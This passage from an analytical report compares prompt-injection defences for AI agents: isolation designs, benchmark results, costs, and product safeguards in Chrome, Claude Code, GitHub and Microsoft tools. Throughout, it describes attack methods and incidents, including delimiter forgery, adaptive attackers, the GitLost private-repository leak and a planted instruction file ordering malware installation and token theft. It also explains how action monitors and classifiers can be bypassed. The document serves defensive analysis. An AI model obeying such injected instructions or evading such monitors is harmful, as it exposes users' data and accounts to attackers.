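| LLMbda agent | 75.0% | 75.0% | 64.6% |
| LLMbda agent, endorsement off | not tested | 62.5% | 54.2% |
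| CaMeL, policies off | 66.7% | not tested | 70.8% |
| CaMeL, policies on | 37.5% | not tested | 37.5% |

The LLMbda agent did about as well as CaMeL without policies, and turning the policies on nearly halved CaMeL's score. With only 16 tasks, each score has a margin of error of about 20 points or more, which is too wide to tell whether the LLMbda agent or CaMeL without policies is better. Garby and colleagues cite a comparable fall for TypeGuard, the system from *Language-Based Agent Control*. It completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks without policies and 8 with them.

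The LLMbda agent avoids much of this loss because its plan can endorse untrusted data. Suppose the user asks it to read a file and pay the bill inside. The agent decides to trust the file's contents before it opens the file, so an injection can't influence that decision. It also tests its plan on a simulated bank and corrects any errors before it sees real data, though each correction needs another model call.

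Endorsement also led to the two successful attacks in 1,296 attacked runs. Both runs used GPT-5.2, and in both the agent endorsed payment details from a file whose contents the attacker had replaced. In about two thirds of the runs, planning in advance was generally enough to stop the attack. The other 423 runs are the real test of the labels, and attacks succeeded in about 0.5% of them.

An attack of the same kind succeeded in the original CaMeL evaluation, and CaMeL's developers placed it outside their threat model. That fairly reflects what labels can do, but a company that wants an agent to pay bills from files still needs another way to check the payee.

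### Measured waiting times

There is little good evidence on speed. *A Survey on Agentic Security* (2025) found that only 18 of 92 papers on defences reported their costs comprehensively. Costa and colleagues say that FIDES's extra steps add delay, but they report no timings and did not try to make the system fast.

Most of the timings for CaMeL come from papers that propose a rival defence. The most recent is *ToolFence* (2026), published in September. *AttriGuard* (2026) timed two models under attack. *Indirect Prompt Injections* (2025) and *Agent-Sentry* (2026) also timed CaMeL, but without a matching time for an undefended agent. These are average times per task:

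| Source | Model or tasks | Undefended | CaMeL | Ratio |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| *ToolFence* | Qwen3-max, 200 AgentDojo runs | 6.3 s | 81.7 s | 12.9 |
| *AttriGuard* | Gemini 2.5 Flash, AgentDojo under attack | 11.5 s | 165.5 s | 14.4 |
| *AttriGuard* | Llama 3.3 70B, AgentDojo under attack | 14.2 s | 105.4 s | 7.4 |
| *Indirect Prompt Injections* | GPT-4o, Banking and Slack, no attack | not given | 32.8 s | – |
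| *Agent-Sentry* | Tasks from AgentDojo and another benchmark, AgentDyn | not given | 26.6 s | – |

In the available comparisons, CaMeL took 7 to 14 times as long as the undefended agent. The text of *AttriGuard* gives a larger increase, of one to two orders of magnitude. Even a 7- to 14-fold delay is serious for a user waiting for a response, though it may not matter for an overnight job.

Rival defences are faster but offer weaker assurance. The AttriGuard system repeats each step with a toned-down copy of the untrusted text and blocks any tool call the agent doesn't make again. It took 32 seconds with Gemini and 41 with Llama, about three times as long as with no defence. When an attacker could make up to 200 attempts at each of 61 cases, the attack eventually worked in 6.6% of cases against the Gemini agent and 9.8% against the Llama agent. This test did not include CaMeL.

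### Counting the calls in one task

In one AgentDojo task, the agent must check a hotel's reviews and book a room if the hotel is rated above 4. An ordinary agent can do this in three model calls. It requests the reviews in the first, reads them and requests the booking in the second, and replies to the user in the third. Each call depends on the one before, so they can't run in parallel.

Costa and colleagues published a FIDES run of the same task, which took ten calls:

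1. The privileged model requests the reviews, and the software hides the result in a variable.
2. The privileged model puts three questions to the quarantined model, one at a time. This takes three calls to each model, and the last answer says whether the rating is above 4.
3. The privileged model asks to see that answer.
4. It requests the booking.
5. It replies to the user.

The instructions limited the planner to requesting one piece of information at a time. If it could send all three questions together, the quarantined model could answer them in parallel, and the run would take eight calls, with only six in sequence.

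CaMeL's privileged model writes one program that handles both outcomes. The program could call the quarantined model twice, once to summarise the reviews and once to give a yes/no answer about the rating. Neither call depends on the other, so they could run in parallel. The interpreter then makes the booking and displays the reply without another model call.

The comparison of waiting times below assumes that a short call takes 2 seconds and writing a program takes 10. The times and call counts are illustrative, except for the ten calls in the published FIDES run.

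| Design | Total model calls | Calls in sequence | Waiting time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent loop | 3 | 3 | 6 s |
| FIDES, one question at a time | 10 | 10 | 20 s |
| FIDES, three questions in parallel | 8 | 6 | 12 s |
| CaMeL, first program works | 3 | 2 | 12 s |
| CaMeL, third program works | 5 | 4 | 32 s |

The last row assumes that the first two programs fail before they reach either question. *ToolFence* attributes CaMeL's long delays to repeated code generation. The number of calls is therefore a poor guide to speed. CaMeL can make three calls, like the ordinary agent, and still take much longer, because a program is long and may need several attempts.

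### What the extra text costs

Model providers usually charge by the token, and output tokens generally cost more than input tokens. In *AttriGuard*'s tests with Gemini, the undefended agent used about 11,900 input tokens and 800 output tokens per task, while CaMeL used about 126,600 input tokens and 22,700 output tokens. At illustrative prices of $1 per million input tokens and $5 per million output tokens, 1,000 such tasks would cost about $16 with the undefended agent and $240 with CaMeL.

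A typical task may cost much less than the average. In *Indirect Prompt Injections*, CaMeL's average input was 3.6 times that of the undefended agent, but its median input was only 1.8 times as high. A few difficult tasks therefore account for much of the expense. Limiting retries would save money but cause some tasks to fail.

*Taxonomy, Evaluation and Exploitation of IPI-Centric LLM Agent Defense Frameworks* (2025) puts dual-LLM designs among the slower defences but calls their extra token use minimal. The token claim doesn't fit either set of measurements for CaMeL, though it may be true of lighter designs. *Think Twice Before You Act* (2026) describes a system that plans in isolation to protect agents from malicious tool descriptions. On AgentDojo's harmless tasks, it used only 45% more tokens than an undefended agent.

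*Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) suggests two ways to reduce the number of model calls. The software can store a plan known to be safe and reuse it when the same request recurs. It can also combine many small questions into one, for example by having the quarantined model extract the amounts from 100 receipts in a single call. The paper reports that caching, combined with ordinary software for reading data in fixed formats, cut tokens and waiting time by up to half, but the evidence is an unpublished internal test.

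Reusing a plan seems safe if the tools and policies haven't changed. Combining the receipts in one call weakens the isolation, because an injection in one receipt can then change the amounts the model reports for the other 99. The map-reduce pattern uses a separate call for each file to prevent this. Developers can often reduce the delay by running those calls in parallel, but the company still pays for every call.

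### The work of connecting each tool

An ordinary agent can use a poorly documented tool because the model receives the tool's output. A planner that never receives the output needs a description of its structure in advance. In the earlier program for paying a bill, the privileged model wrote `payment.account` before the agent had opened the file. This works only if the model already has the field's name. Developers therefore have to document the fields and types that each tool returns, and update the documentation whenever the tool changes.

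Someone also has to label the data that tools return. For FIDES, Costa and colleagues wrote wrappers, small programs that label each part of a tool's result. The wrappers went only one level deep, so a record inside another record got a single label for all its contents. That was enough for AgentDojo, but a company's customer database may need finer labels to avoid hiding harmless fields.

Setting policies also takes work. Costa and colleagues assigned one of three policies to each of 27 tools. They also wrote long instructions to teach the planner how to use variables, and adjusted these by hand on the Workspace tasks with GPT-4o. They reused the same instructions for the other suites and for o1. Labels are harder to reuse when a company adds a new tool, because somebody has to decide who could have written each field.

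### Why scores from different papers don't form a ranking

Published scores for CaMeL include 31.0% in *Agent-Sentry*, 38.0% with Gemini in *AttriGuard*, and 43.1% with Qwen3-max in *ToolFence*. Garby and colleagues report 37.5% and 66.7% with GPT-5.2, and these two scores differ only in whether the policies were on. The other scores also differ in model and tasks.

The choice of tasks can affect completion rates as much as the choice of defence. *AttriGuard* removed four AgentDojo tasks, some because the user explicitly asks the agent to follow untrusted content. Isolation handles such tasks badly, so leaving them out probably raises CaMeL's score. In *Agent-Sentry*'s tests, Progent, a defence that checks tool calls against hand-written rules, completed 93.7% of tasks on one benchmark and 69.2% on another.

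A defence can even help a model complete more tasks by fixing a weakness unrelated to prompt injection. In *AttriGuard*'s tests, Gemini completed 57.6% of tasks without a defence and 73.9% with IPIGuard, which plans the order of tool calls in advance. The undefended model often stopped to ask the user for the current time, and the fixed plan made it carry on. This gain is therefore weak evidence of how IPIGuard would affect task completion in a model that doesn't stop to ask.

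Researchers also count attempts differently. Costa and colleagues averaged five runs, and Garby and colleagues averaged three. Foerster and colleagues counted a task as completed if any of five attempts succeeded, which gives a much higher number for the same agent. Scoring errors also make results harder to compare. *Indirect Prompt Injections* describes a Slack task that asks the agent to send Alice a message. The original check required her inbox to grow by exactly one message, so if an attack also sent her one, the task was marked as failed even though the agent had delivered the right message.

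Timings vary at least as much. *ToolFence* reports 6.3 seconds for an undefended agent using Qwen3-max, while *AgentSentry* (2026, a different paper from *Agent-Sentry*) reports 26.4 seconds for an undefended agent on attacked Workspace tasks. For IPIGuard, *A Survey on Agentic Security* quotes 13.9 seconds per task, but *AttriGuard* measured 51.5 seconds with one model and 102.9 with another. The load on a provider's servers can also affect timings.

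A fair comparison tests both designs with the same model, tasks, policies and number of attempts, and includes an undefended agent. Garby and colleagues met most of these conditions when they reran CaMeL, but they didn't include an ordinary agent loop. Many of their CaMeL runs under attack also didn't finish, so with GPT-5.2 and policies on, they could score utility for only 233 of 432 runs.

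## Do better-trained models make isolation unnecessary?

Isolation is expensive because it has to work even when a model obeys text it was only meant to read. If developers could train a model never to do that, an ordinary agent loop would be safe, complete more tasks and cost less. Models in 2026 resist prompt injection much better than the 2024 models in the early isolation papers, but developers have only measured how often they fail, and nobody has proved an upper limit on that rate.

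### Marking, training and filtering

The easiest alternative to isolation is to leave everything in one context and mark the untrusted text. Spotlighting puts markers around a tool's result, or encodes it, to show the model where the text came from. Peters-Gill and colleagues also mention sandwich prompting, which repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. Both methods depend on the model following the marks. An attacker may also be able to forge them, for example by ending the marked text early and adding what looks like a new message from the user. Random markers make forgery harder, but the model still has to read the injection to do its job.

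Developers can also train the model to rank instructions by source. The developer's rules come first, the user's request comes second, and text from a tool has no authority. A training example might pair a request with a web page containing an injection, and reward the model for finishing the request and ignoring the injection. The model learns a strong habit this way, but only from the attacks in its training. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues compare the problem with image recognition, where researchers have worked for more than a decade to defend classifiers against images altered to fool them and still have no complete solution.

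A filter is a separate program, usually another model, that looks for attacks. Some filters delete suspicious instructions from text and keep the rest. Anthropic, the developer of the Claude models, uses what it calls probes to inspect tool results before the agent acts on them. In some products it adds a classifier that blocks dangerous tool calls, so an attack has to get past both. But filters make mistakes too, and an attacker who can test them can look for wording they miss, as the attacker against WebMCP-Phalanx did.

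A guarantee that a trained model will resist prompt injection would have to cover every text an attacker could write, and no one knows how to check a model against all of them.

### The case for relying on the model

The best evidence for trusting the model comes from a benchmark that Gray Swan, an AI security testing company, built with the British and American governments' AI institutes and several developers. It replays injections that people wrote in public competitions. The scenarios cover coding, tool use and operating a computer through its screen, and the attackers have goals such as stealing data or moving money.

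Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1, published in September, reports results on 1,804 of these attacks. The July card for Claude Opus 5 used an earlier set of 1,130. The table gives an attacker's chance of succeeding in one attempt and within 15.

| Model | Card | 1 attempt | 15 attempts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | September | 0.1% | 1.0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | September | 0.4% | 4.8% |
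| Gemini 3.7 Flash | September | not given | 9.2% |
| Claude Opus 5 | July | 0.2% | 2.0% |
| Muse Spark | July | not given | 16.5% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | July | 3.1% | 20.0% |

Five of 7,124 runs with Fable 5.1 ended in a successful attack. The model was most vulnerable when operating a computer through the screen, where an attacker with 15 attempts had a 4.1% chance of success, compared with 0.3% for coding and 0.0% for tool use.

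Filters can lower attack success rates further. Anthropic also tested browser agents in 110 simulated environments, with ten attempts at each. Without filters, attacks on Fable 5.1 succeeded at least once in ten of the environments. With the probes and the action classifier on, no attacks succeeded. Opus 5 had done equally well with filters in July, across 129 environments, a result The Decoder reported under the optimistic title *Opus 5 may have solved browser-based prompt injection*. Willison (2026) quotes Boris Cherny of Anthropic calling Opus 5 "our least prompt injectable model yet".

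These figures, including those for competitors' models, come from Anthropic's own cards. Other developers may not publish comparable tests. According to VentureBeat, OpenAI's April card for GPT-5.5 covers only known attacks on connectors, which link the model to outside services, and reports a robustness score instead of an attack success rate.

Still, a developer could reasonably question whether isolation is worthwhile against an attack that works once in a thousand attempts, when it can stop even a strong model from completing about a quarter of its tasks. Peters-Gill and colleagues' own benchmark supports this doubt, since attacks on GPT-5.5 succeeded 0.0% of the time without isolation.

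A model that resists an attack may still fail to complete the user's task. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark of 19 models, found that attacks compromised Claude Haiku 4.5 in only 8.4% of runs, but the share of tasks it completed fell from 75.0% to 52.6% when an injection was present.

### Attackers who adapt

A fixed benchmark replays attacks that people wrote against other models. Anthropic's September card leaves out models that the competitors had targeted, because attacks tailored to a model usually work better on it. This makes the comparison fairer, but it also means that none of the injections were written to attack the models with low scores. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr et al., October 2025) found that attackers who adapt to a defence can get past defences that do well against fixed attacks.

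*How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports on a competition in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 leading models. Participants could read the agent's response, revise the injection and try again. Their attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Even against Opus 4.5, they found an attack that worked in 13 of 37 scenarios.

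In most scenarios, an attack counted as successful only if the agent also hid it from the user. For example, a user asks an assistant to check for urgent emails, and a marketing email contains an instruction to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. The user gets an ordinary summary and misses the deadline. Gemini 2.5 Pro took the harmful action in about 16% of attempts, roughly twice the official success rate of attacks against it, so the official rates understate how often agents took harmful actions.

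In other ways the competition made attacks easier. Attackers saw the conversation before writing the injection and knew which tool call they had to cause, so Dziemian and colleagues treat the success rates as an upper bound for single-turn attacks. Most of the models also ran without extended reasoning, and all are now at least a generation old.

Forging the syntax and delimiters that separate messages was among the most successful attack strategies against both GPT and Claude models, which weakens the case for marking as a defence. One attack template, which told the model that it was in a simulation with a control panel, worked in 21 scenarios and on nine models with only small changes.

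Attacks that beat Opus 4.5 also worked on the other models 44% to 81% of the time. But none of the tested attacks that beat Qwen3 VL, one of the weaker models, worked on Opus 4.5. A benchmark made mostly of attacks on weak models can therefore make a strong model look almost immune.

Anthropic's September card includes a harder test of newer models. Shade, an automated attacker from Gray Swan, gets 200 attempts at each of 40 coding scenarios. Gray Swan recently trained a stronger version of Shade for longer and on more varied attacks. Each cell in the table gives the share of attempts that succeeded and the number of scenarios with at least one success. All three models used extended reasoning.

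| Model | Original Shade | Stronger Shade | Stronger Shade, with probes |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26%, 31 of 40 | 56.87%, 38 of 40 | 12.80%, 36 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68%, 27 of 40 | 90.93%, 40 of 40 | 18.21%, 40 of 40 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.3%, 7 of 40 | 19.47%, 36 of 40 | 15.76%, 35 of 40 |

The model that scored 0.4% on fixed attacks scored 90.93% here. The probes blocked most of the attempts that would otherwise have succeeded against Opus 5, but a persistent attacker still got through in every scenario.

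Anthropic reroutes Fable 5.1 requests that trigger its hacking classifier to an older model, Claude Opus 4.8, and about 64% of requests in the stronger test went there. No attack succeeded in the 2,826 requests that Fable 5.1 answered itself, so every successful attack came through the older model. Fable 5.1 may therefore be far more robust than its row suggests, but customers use the whole system, and in this test rerouting requests to guard against hacking made prompt injection easier.

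Anthropic calls the test highly permissive, because Shade trains on the same scenarios it is tested on and a real attacker usually doesn't know the target so well. This is a fair reason not to treat 57% or 91% as a forecast, but it applies less to a popular coding agent, since an attacker can install a copy and practise on it in private.

Buyers also cannot assume that a more capable model is safer. Across the competition's models, Dziemian and colleagues found only a weak and statistically insignificant link between scores on a difficult science test and resistance to injection, and found that the model's family and training mattered more. They conclude that agents also need system-level defences, including isolation of untrusted input.

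### A small rate, many times over

An agent that reads email all day gives attackers many chances. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p* and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is:

1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

If each injection attempt has a 0.1% chance of success and attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in 1,000 attempts is 1 − 0.999¹⁰⁰⁰, or about 63%. The chance is about 10% for 100 attempts and about 95% for 3,000.

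It is hard to show that a model's rate is lower than this. Zero successes in Fable 5.1's 2,826 direct answers would be compatible with a true rate of about 0.1%, even if the answers had been independent trials.

Real attempts aren't independent, because some situations are much harder to attack than others. VentureBeat reports that a single attack on Claude Opus 4.6, operating a computer through its screen without safeguards, worked 17.8% of the time. If attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success would pass 98% after 20 attempts, but it was only 78.6% after 200. In a restricted coding environment, all 200 attempts failed.

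An attack's success also depends on its wording. Dziemian and colleagues found that only 0.5% of all attempts against Opus 4.5 succeeded, but when they reran attacks that had worked on Claude and GPT models, at least half worked again on the same model.

Suppose one injection in 1,000 always works and the others never do. An attacker who picks one at random and emails it to 1,000 people has a 0.1% chance of success, far below the 63% if each email independently had a 0.1% chance of working. But if the injection works, it takes over all 1,000 agents, so the average number of victims is one in both cases. Attackers who can test different injections first have much better odds, because they need only one success to find an injection that works on everyone.

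The defender may also notice a series of failed attacks and block the sender. The 63% is therefore a poor prediction for any particular company, but it shows why a rate of 0.1% is not negligible for an agent that reads thousands of messages.

### What a robust model adds to isolation

A designer can use both approaches. Better training can make the values that a quarantined model returns more reliable, which isolation can't do.

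In the earlier example of the builder, a hidden instruction to answer "yes" could release $5,000 for unfinished work. A quarantined model that ignores the instruction would answer "no", and the money would stay in the account. If the builder lies about the work instead, the same model would correctly report the email's claim, and the agent would pay.

| Attack | Isolation | A robust quarantined model |
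|---|---|---|
| A hidden instruction to forward the mailbox | Prevents the extra tool call | Adds little |
| A hidden instruction to answer "yes" | Doesn't help | Can make it less likely |
| A hidden instruction to return the attacker's address instead of Bob's | Needs a policy on recipients | Can make it less likely |
| A hidden instruction to copy private notes into a reply | Needs labels and a policy | Can make it less likely |
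| A false account number in a bill | Needs a policy or a trusted record | Doesn't help |

Filters can also help here by checking a document before the quarantined model reads it. Training matters even more when a design lets the privileged model read some untrusted text, as FIDES does when its planner inspects a hidden value, because the only protections left are the model's resistance to injection and the policies on its tools.

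Resistance to one kind of injection doesn't imply resistance to another. *When the Spec Sheet Lies* (2026) tested models that write compliance documents from material containing injections. Attacks that tried to override GPT-4o's instructions worked 30% of the time, but attacks that tried to make it falsify the document worked every time. Against Claude Sonnet 5, override attacks worked 0% of the time and data theft attacks 2%, but the average success rate across all the attacks was 10.7%, so at least one other kind must have worked much more often.

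Falsification is the closest of these to the attacks that isolation doesn't prevent. The benchmarks in Anthropic's cards mostly measure whether an agent takes a harmful action, which a quarantined model can't do. Someone choosing a quarantined model would need to measure how often an injection makes it return a wrong date, address or answer.

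## Which products separate contexts today?

As of October 2026, several widely used products have borrowed parts of these designs. Google's Chrome browser isolates a model that checks the agent's actions, and Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, reads most web pages in isolation. GitHub, the code-hosting service, isolates credentials and the power to make changes. Microsoft offers developers the two-model split with labels as an experimental option. None of these products keeps all untrusted text away from the model that requests tool calls unless a developer turns on that protection.

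### Chrome isolates the checker

The model that plans Chrome's actions reads the pages it works on, so an injection on a page can reach it. Google marks untrusted text and trains the model on known attacks. It has also added a second model, the User Alignment Critic, partly inspired by the dual-LLM pattern and CaMeL (Parker, 2025, *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome*).

Chrome reverses Willison's arrangement. Its planner, the model that reads untrusted text, requests every action, and an isolated model called the critic can only approve or reject each one. The critic sees metadata about the action but no unfiltered web content. If a page tricks the planner into trying to open the user's email during a shopping task, the critic should reject the action because it doesn't serve the user's goal. The planner then gets feedback and tries again, and after repeated failures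 it can return control to the user.

This protection depends on the critic's judgement, so it doesn't guarantee control-flow integrity. The critic also can't detect an action that fits the task but rests on false information, such as buying the T-shirt that a fake review recommends. An attacker who controls the planner may be able to influence what the critic reads, because the planner writes the proposed action. Parker claims only that the web can't poison the critic directly.

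Chrome also limits which websites the agent can use for a task. The full design has one list of sites the agent may read and another of sites where it may also click and type. The component that approves sites never sees web content. If a page includes an advert from an unlisted site, the browser doesn't show it to the model. Google's first version had only the second list, because its developers wanted to see how the limits affected real tasks. Berschadski (2026) describes the critic and the site limits again in *Future Mode Part 2*, but doesn't say whether Chrome now has both lists.

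Some of Chrome's checks don't need a model. Software checks each site against a list of sensitive ones, such as banks, and asks the user before the agent visits a site on the list. It also restricts web addresses written by the model to known public ones, to prevent data theft. Before a purchase, however, Parker says only that the agent will "try to pause". Google measures attack success rates in its own tests, but Parker gives no figures.

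### Claude Code isolates most web pages

Claude Code's WebFetch tool takes a web address and a question about the page. Anthropic says "for most fetches" a separate model call reads the page and answers the question, and the main model receives only the answer. The tool's documentation doesn't list the exceptions. Anthropic's security page describes the separate context as a way to keep malicious prompts out of the main one.

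Besides using WebFetch, the main model can download an unprocessed page with an ordinary command, although in Manual mode the user has to approve this first. Files, command output and results from outside tools also go straight into the main context. An injection in a downloaded project's documentation can therefore reach a model that edits files and runs commands.

Claude Code's auto mode adds a checker similar to Chrome's. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes a classifier that receives the user's messages and the agent's tool calls, but not the tool results or the agent's explanations. It approves or blocks actions in place of the user, who would have approved 93% of them. Edits to files inside the project skip this check because developers can review them later.

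In Anthropic's tests, the classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary tool calls. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 artificial attempts to send data out, and 17% of 52 real actions where an agent had gone beyond the user's request. None of these figures directly measures resistance to prompt injection. Anthropic has nevertheless made auto mode the default for four of its plans, according to *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, so more users now rely on the classifier.

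### Why a summary doesn't block reinjection

Willison warned that one model's answer can carry an injection into another model's context. WebFetch and the web tool in Strands Agents, a toolkit for building agents, both allow this because they return free text. By default, the Strands tool uses a separate "analyst" agent to read the page and answer a question about it, so the full page never enters the main context.

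Suppose a coding agent uses a second model to look up which version of a library fixes a bug, and an attacker has planted an injection in the page that model reads. The injection can instruct the second model to give the version number and add that the project must change a certain setting first. The main model receives this as the answer to its question and has the tools to change the setting. The attack may fail because it has to work on both models, but no software rule prevents it.

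Constraining the answer would block the injection, as Willison's fixed categories do. The software could accept only three whole numbers, such as 4.2.1, which can't contain an instruction. The attacker could still make the agent install a vulnerable version. The software has to enforce the format, because if the main model only asks WebFetch for a version number "and nothing else", an injection can make the reader ignore that request.

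Claude Code's subagents, which handle parts of a task in their own contexts, need more caution than WebFetch. By default, a subagent inherits every tool available to subagents, so an injection can make it do harm before it returns anything. A developer can remove the dangerous tools, but the subagent still returns its result as free text. In auto mode, the classifier reviews the subagent's actions before the result goes back. If the classifier finds a problem, Claude Code adds a warning to the result but still passes it on.

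### Microsoft offers FIDES as an option

In May 2026, Microsoft released a version of FIDES in Agent Framework, its toolkit for developers. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) describes it as experimental, and developers have to switch it on. By default, it then hides all untrusted tool results from the main model and leaves them for a quarantined model to process. Developers can turn the hiding off and keep only the labels and policies.

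The main agent then works from summaries, so free text can reach it here too. But the software labels the summaries as untrusted, so a policy can still refuse a tool call if a summary misleads the main model. WebFetch's documentation describes no such label. Microsoft lists constrained answers among its future plans.

This protection depends on how developers configure it. If they forget to label a tool, the software treats its results as trusted and public. Microsoft is asking developers whether the default should be stricter. In its own example, Microsoft says the agent can't post a comment while untrusted content is in scope, but the sample code gives the comment tool only a secrecy limit. With those settings, an injection could apparently still make the agent post a misleading comment, as long as the agent hadn't read anything private.

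Microsoft and GitHub have also added experimental labels to Copilot CLI, a coding agent that runs in a terminal. Copilot CLI keeps one label for the whole context and checks it before certain calls to GitHub's tools. The check doesn't yet cover all of those tools, or any from other suppliers. GitHub's server labels text from public repositories as untrusted and text from private ones as trusted, so if an employee copied an outsider's message into a private repository, it would be wrongly labelled as trusted.

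Office assistants have the least documentation. Microsoft has a prototype that labels data from some of its mail and chat tools, but it doesn't say in either of its posts whether Microsoft 365 Copilot, its main office assistant, uses FIDES. Berschadski mentions that Google's Gemini Spark assistant now works with Chrome, but doesn't explain how the assistant handles untrusted text.

### GitHub separates the power to write

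GitHub's Agentic Workflows run a coding agent automatically in response to events in a repository, such as a new bug report. GitHub's *Under the hood* (2026) describes strong process isolation around the agent, which still reads untrusted text and chooses its own tool calls. The agent can read from GitHub but can only propose changes. After it exits, ordinary software checks the kind and number of changes, and can remove web addresses and secrets. A separate job with limited permissions then applies what remains. GitHub's *Safe Outputs MCP Gateway Specification* requires this separation of write permissions from the model's reasoning.

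The products also keep credentials in different places:

| Product | Where credentials sit | What a model decides |
|---|---|---|
| Chrome | In the password manager, which the model can't read, although the agent can use sites where the user is logged in | Whether an action serves the user's goal |
| Claude Code on the user's computer | In the macOS Keychain when available, or behind file permissions on Windows and Linux | In auto mode, whether most risky actions may run |
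| Claude Code in Anthropic's cloud | The sandbox has a limited credential, which a proxy exchanges for the real GitHub token | In auto mode, the same |
| GitHub Agentic Workflows | In a gateway and a proxy outside the agent's container | What to read and which changes to propose |
| Agent Framework with FIDES | Microsoft's announcement doesn't say | What to attempt, while software checks the labels |

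### Has anyone adopted the full designs?

In August 2026, SC Media published a sponsored article by a writer at the security company Sophos. It claims that no mainstream agent harness has adopted CaMeL or the dual-LLM design, and names Claude Code, Cursor, Hermes, GitHub Copilot Agent and Gemini CLI.

Claude Code and Copilot CLI don't appear to have a complete design for separating contexts that runs by default. Claude Code's documentation from October still describes free-text answers from WebFetch and direct access to other tool results. Copilot CLI has experimental labels, but Microsoft doesn't describe a quarantined model in it. Whether Cursor, Hermes and Gemini CLI also lack such a design remains unverified.

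But Microsoft had released the two-model split in Agent Framework three months before the article, so the article is wrong if its claim is that nobody has adopted these ideas at all. The toolkit isn't on the article's list, and its availability doesn't show how many developers use it.

Developers mostly say they have adopted separation only partially because stricter isolation would prevent or complicate some work. Parker wants to avoid unnecessary friction for Chrome's users. GitHub says coding agents need broad access to compilers, scripts and repository files, so it gives them a restricted view of the host machine instead of an empty container. Anthropic says sandboxes need new configuration for each capability, and any task requiring network access breaks the isolation. It also warns that WebFetch loses information, because the model reading the page may leave out anything not covered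 by the question.

Microsoft mentions the cost of a second model call and the disadvantage of working from summaries. It advises developers to skip FIDES when an agent has no privileged tools, which seems sensible. These reasons are plausible, but none of the products' developers reports how many tasks its product could no longer complete under full separation.

### A private file in a public comment

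In July 2026, the security company Noma disclosed an attack it named GitLost on GitHub's Agentic Workflows. In the workflow Noma tested, assigning an issue (a bug report or request) triggered an agent, which read the issue and replied with a comment. The agent could also read the organisation's other repositories, including private ones, as InfoQ's *Indirect Prompt Injection Exploits GitHub's AI Agent to Leak Private Repository Data* (2026) reports.

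Noma's researchers posted an issue that looked like a routine request from a sales executive. The agent followed the instructions in it and published a file from a private repository as a comment. No person had to approve the comment, according to SiliconANGLE (2026). This was a demonstration, but Microsoft says it has seen real injection attempts in public repositories that use AI workflows from several suppliers.

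GitHub's separation of credentials and write permissions couldn't be expected to stop this attack. The agent already had permission to read the private file, and the workflow allowed it to post comments, so it didn't need to steal a key. A scan for passwords would not normally block an ordinary document.

A quarantined model that read the issue and returned only a category, such as "bug" or "question", would have prevented the attack, but one that returned a free-text summary might not have. Labels combined with a policy against posting private data in public would also have prevented it. Microsoft says that GitHub's workflows use labels much like those on GitHub's server, but it is unclear whether any labels were active in Noma's test.

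The simplest precaution would have been to deny the agent access to private repositories. Expert Insights' *Researchers Trick Misconfigured GitHub AI Agent Into Leaking a Private Repo* attributes the leak to the configuration, while The Next Web's *‘GitLost’* reports Noma's view that no code change can fix the flaw. Both can be right, since narrower access would have prevented this leak but would not have made the model better at recognising injections.

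### An instruction file from the web

Coding agents often load a file of standing instructions from the folder they start in. TechRadar's *AI agents tricked by a rogue downloads file into running dangerous malware* reports that the security firm Forever Security found a malicious file of this kind in a customer's Downloads folder. The file told the agent to install malware and send out session tokens, which can give access to a logged-in account. The firm says it stopped the attack before any meaningful damage and has reproduced it with both Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex. It couldn't determine how the file got there, but suspects that a compromised website made the browser download it. The article relies on the firm's own account.

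A two-model split would not have helped if the software had still loaded the file as trusted instructions, because the privileged model would have read it. The software would have needed to label the file by its origin and treat anything a website can put in that folder as untrusted. Even after the model had followed the file's instructions, a sandbox could have limited the damage by blocking the agent's access to the session tokens and to unknown servers.
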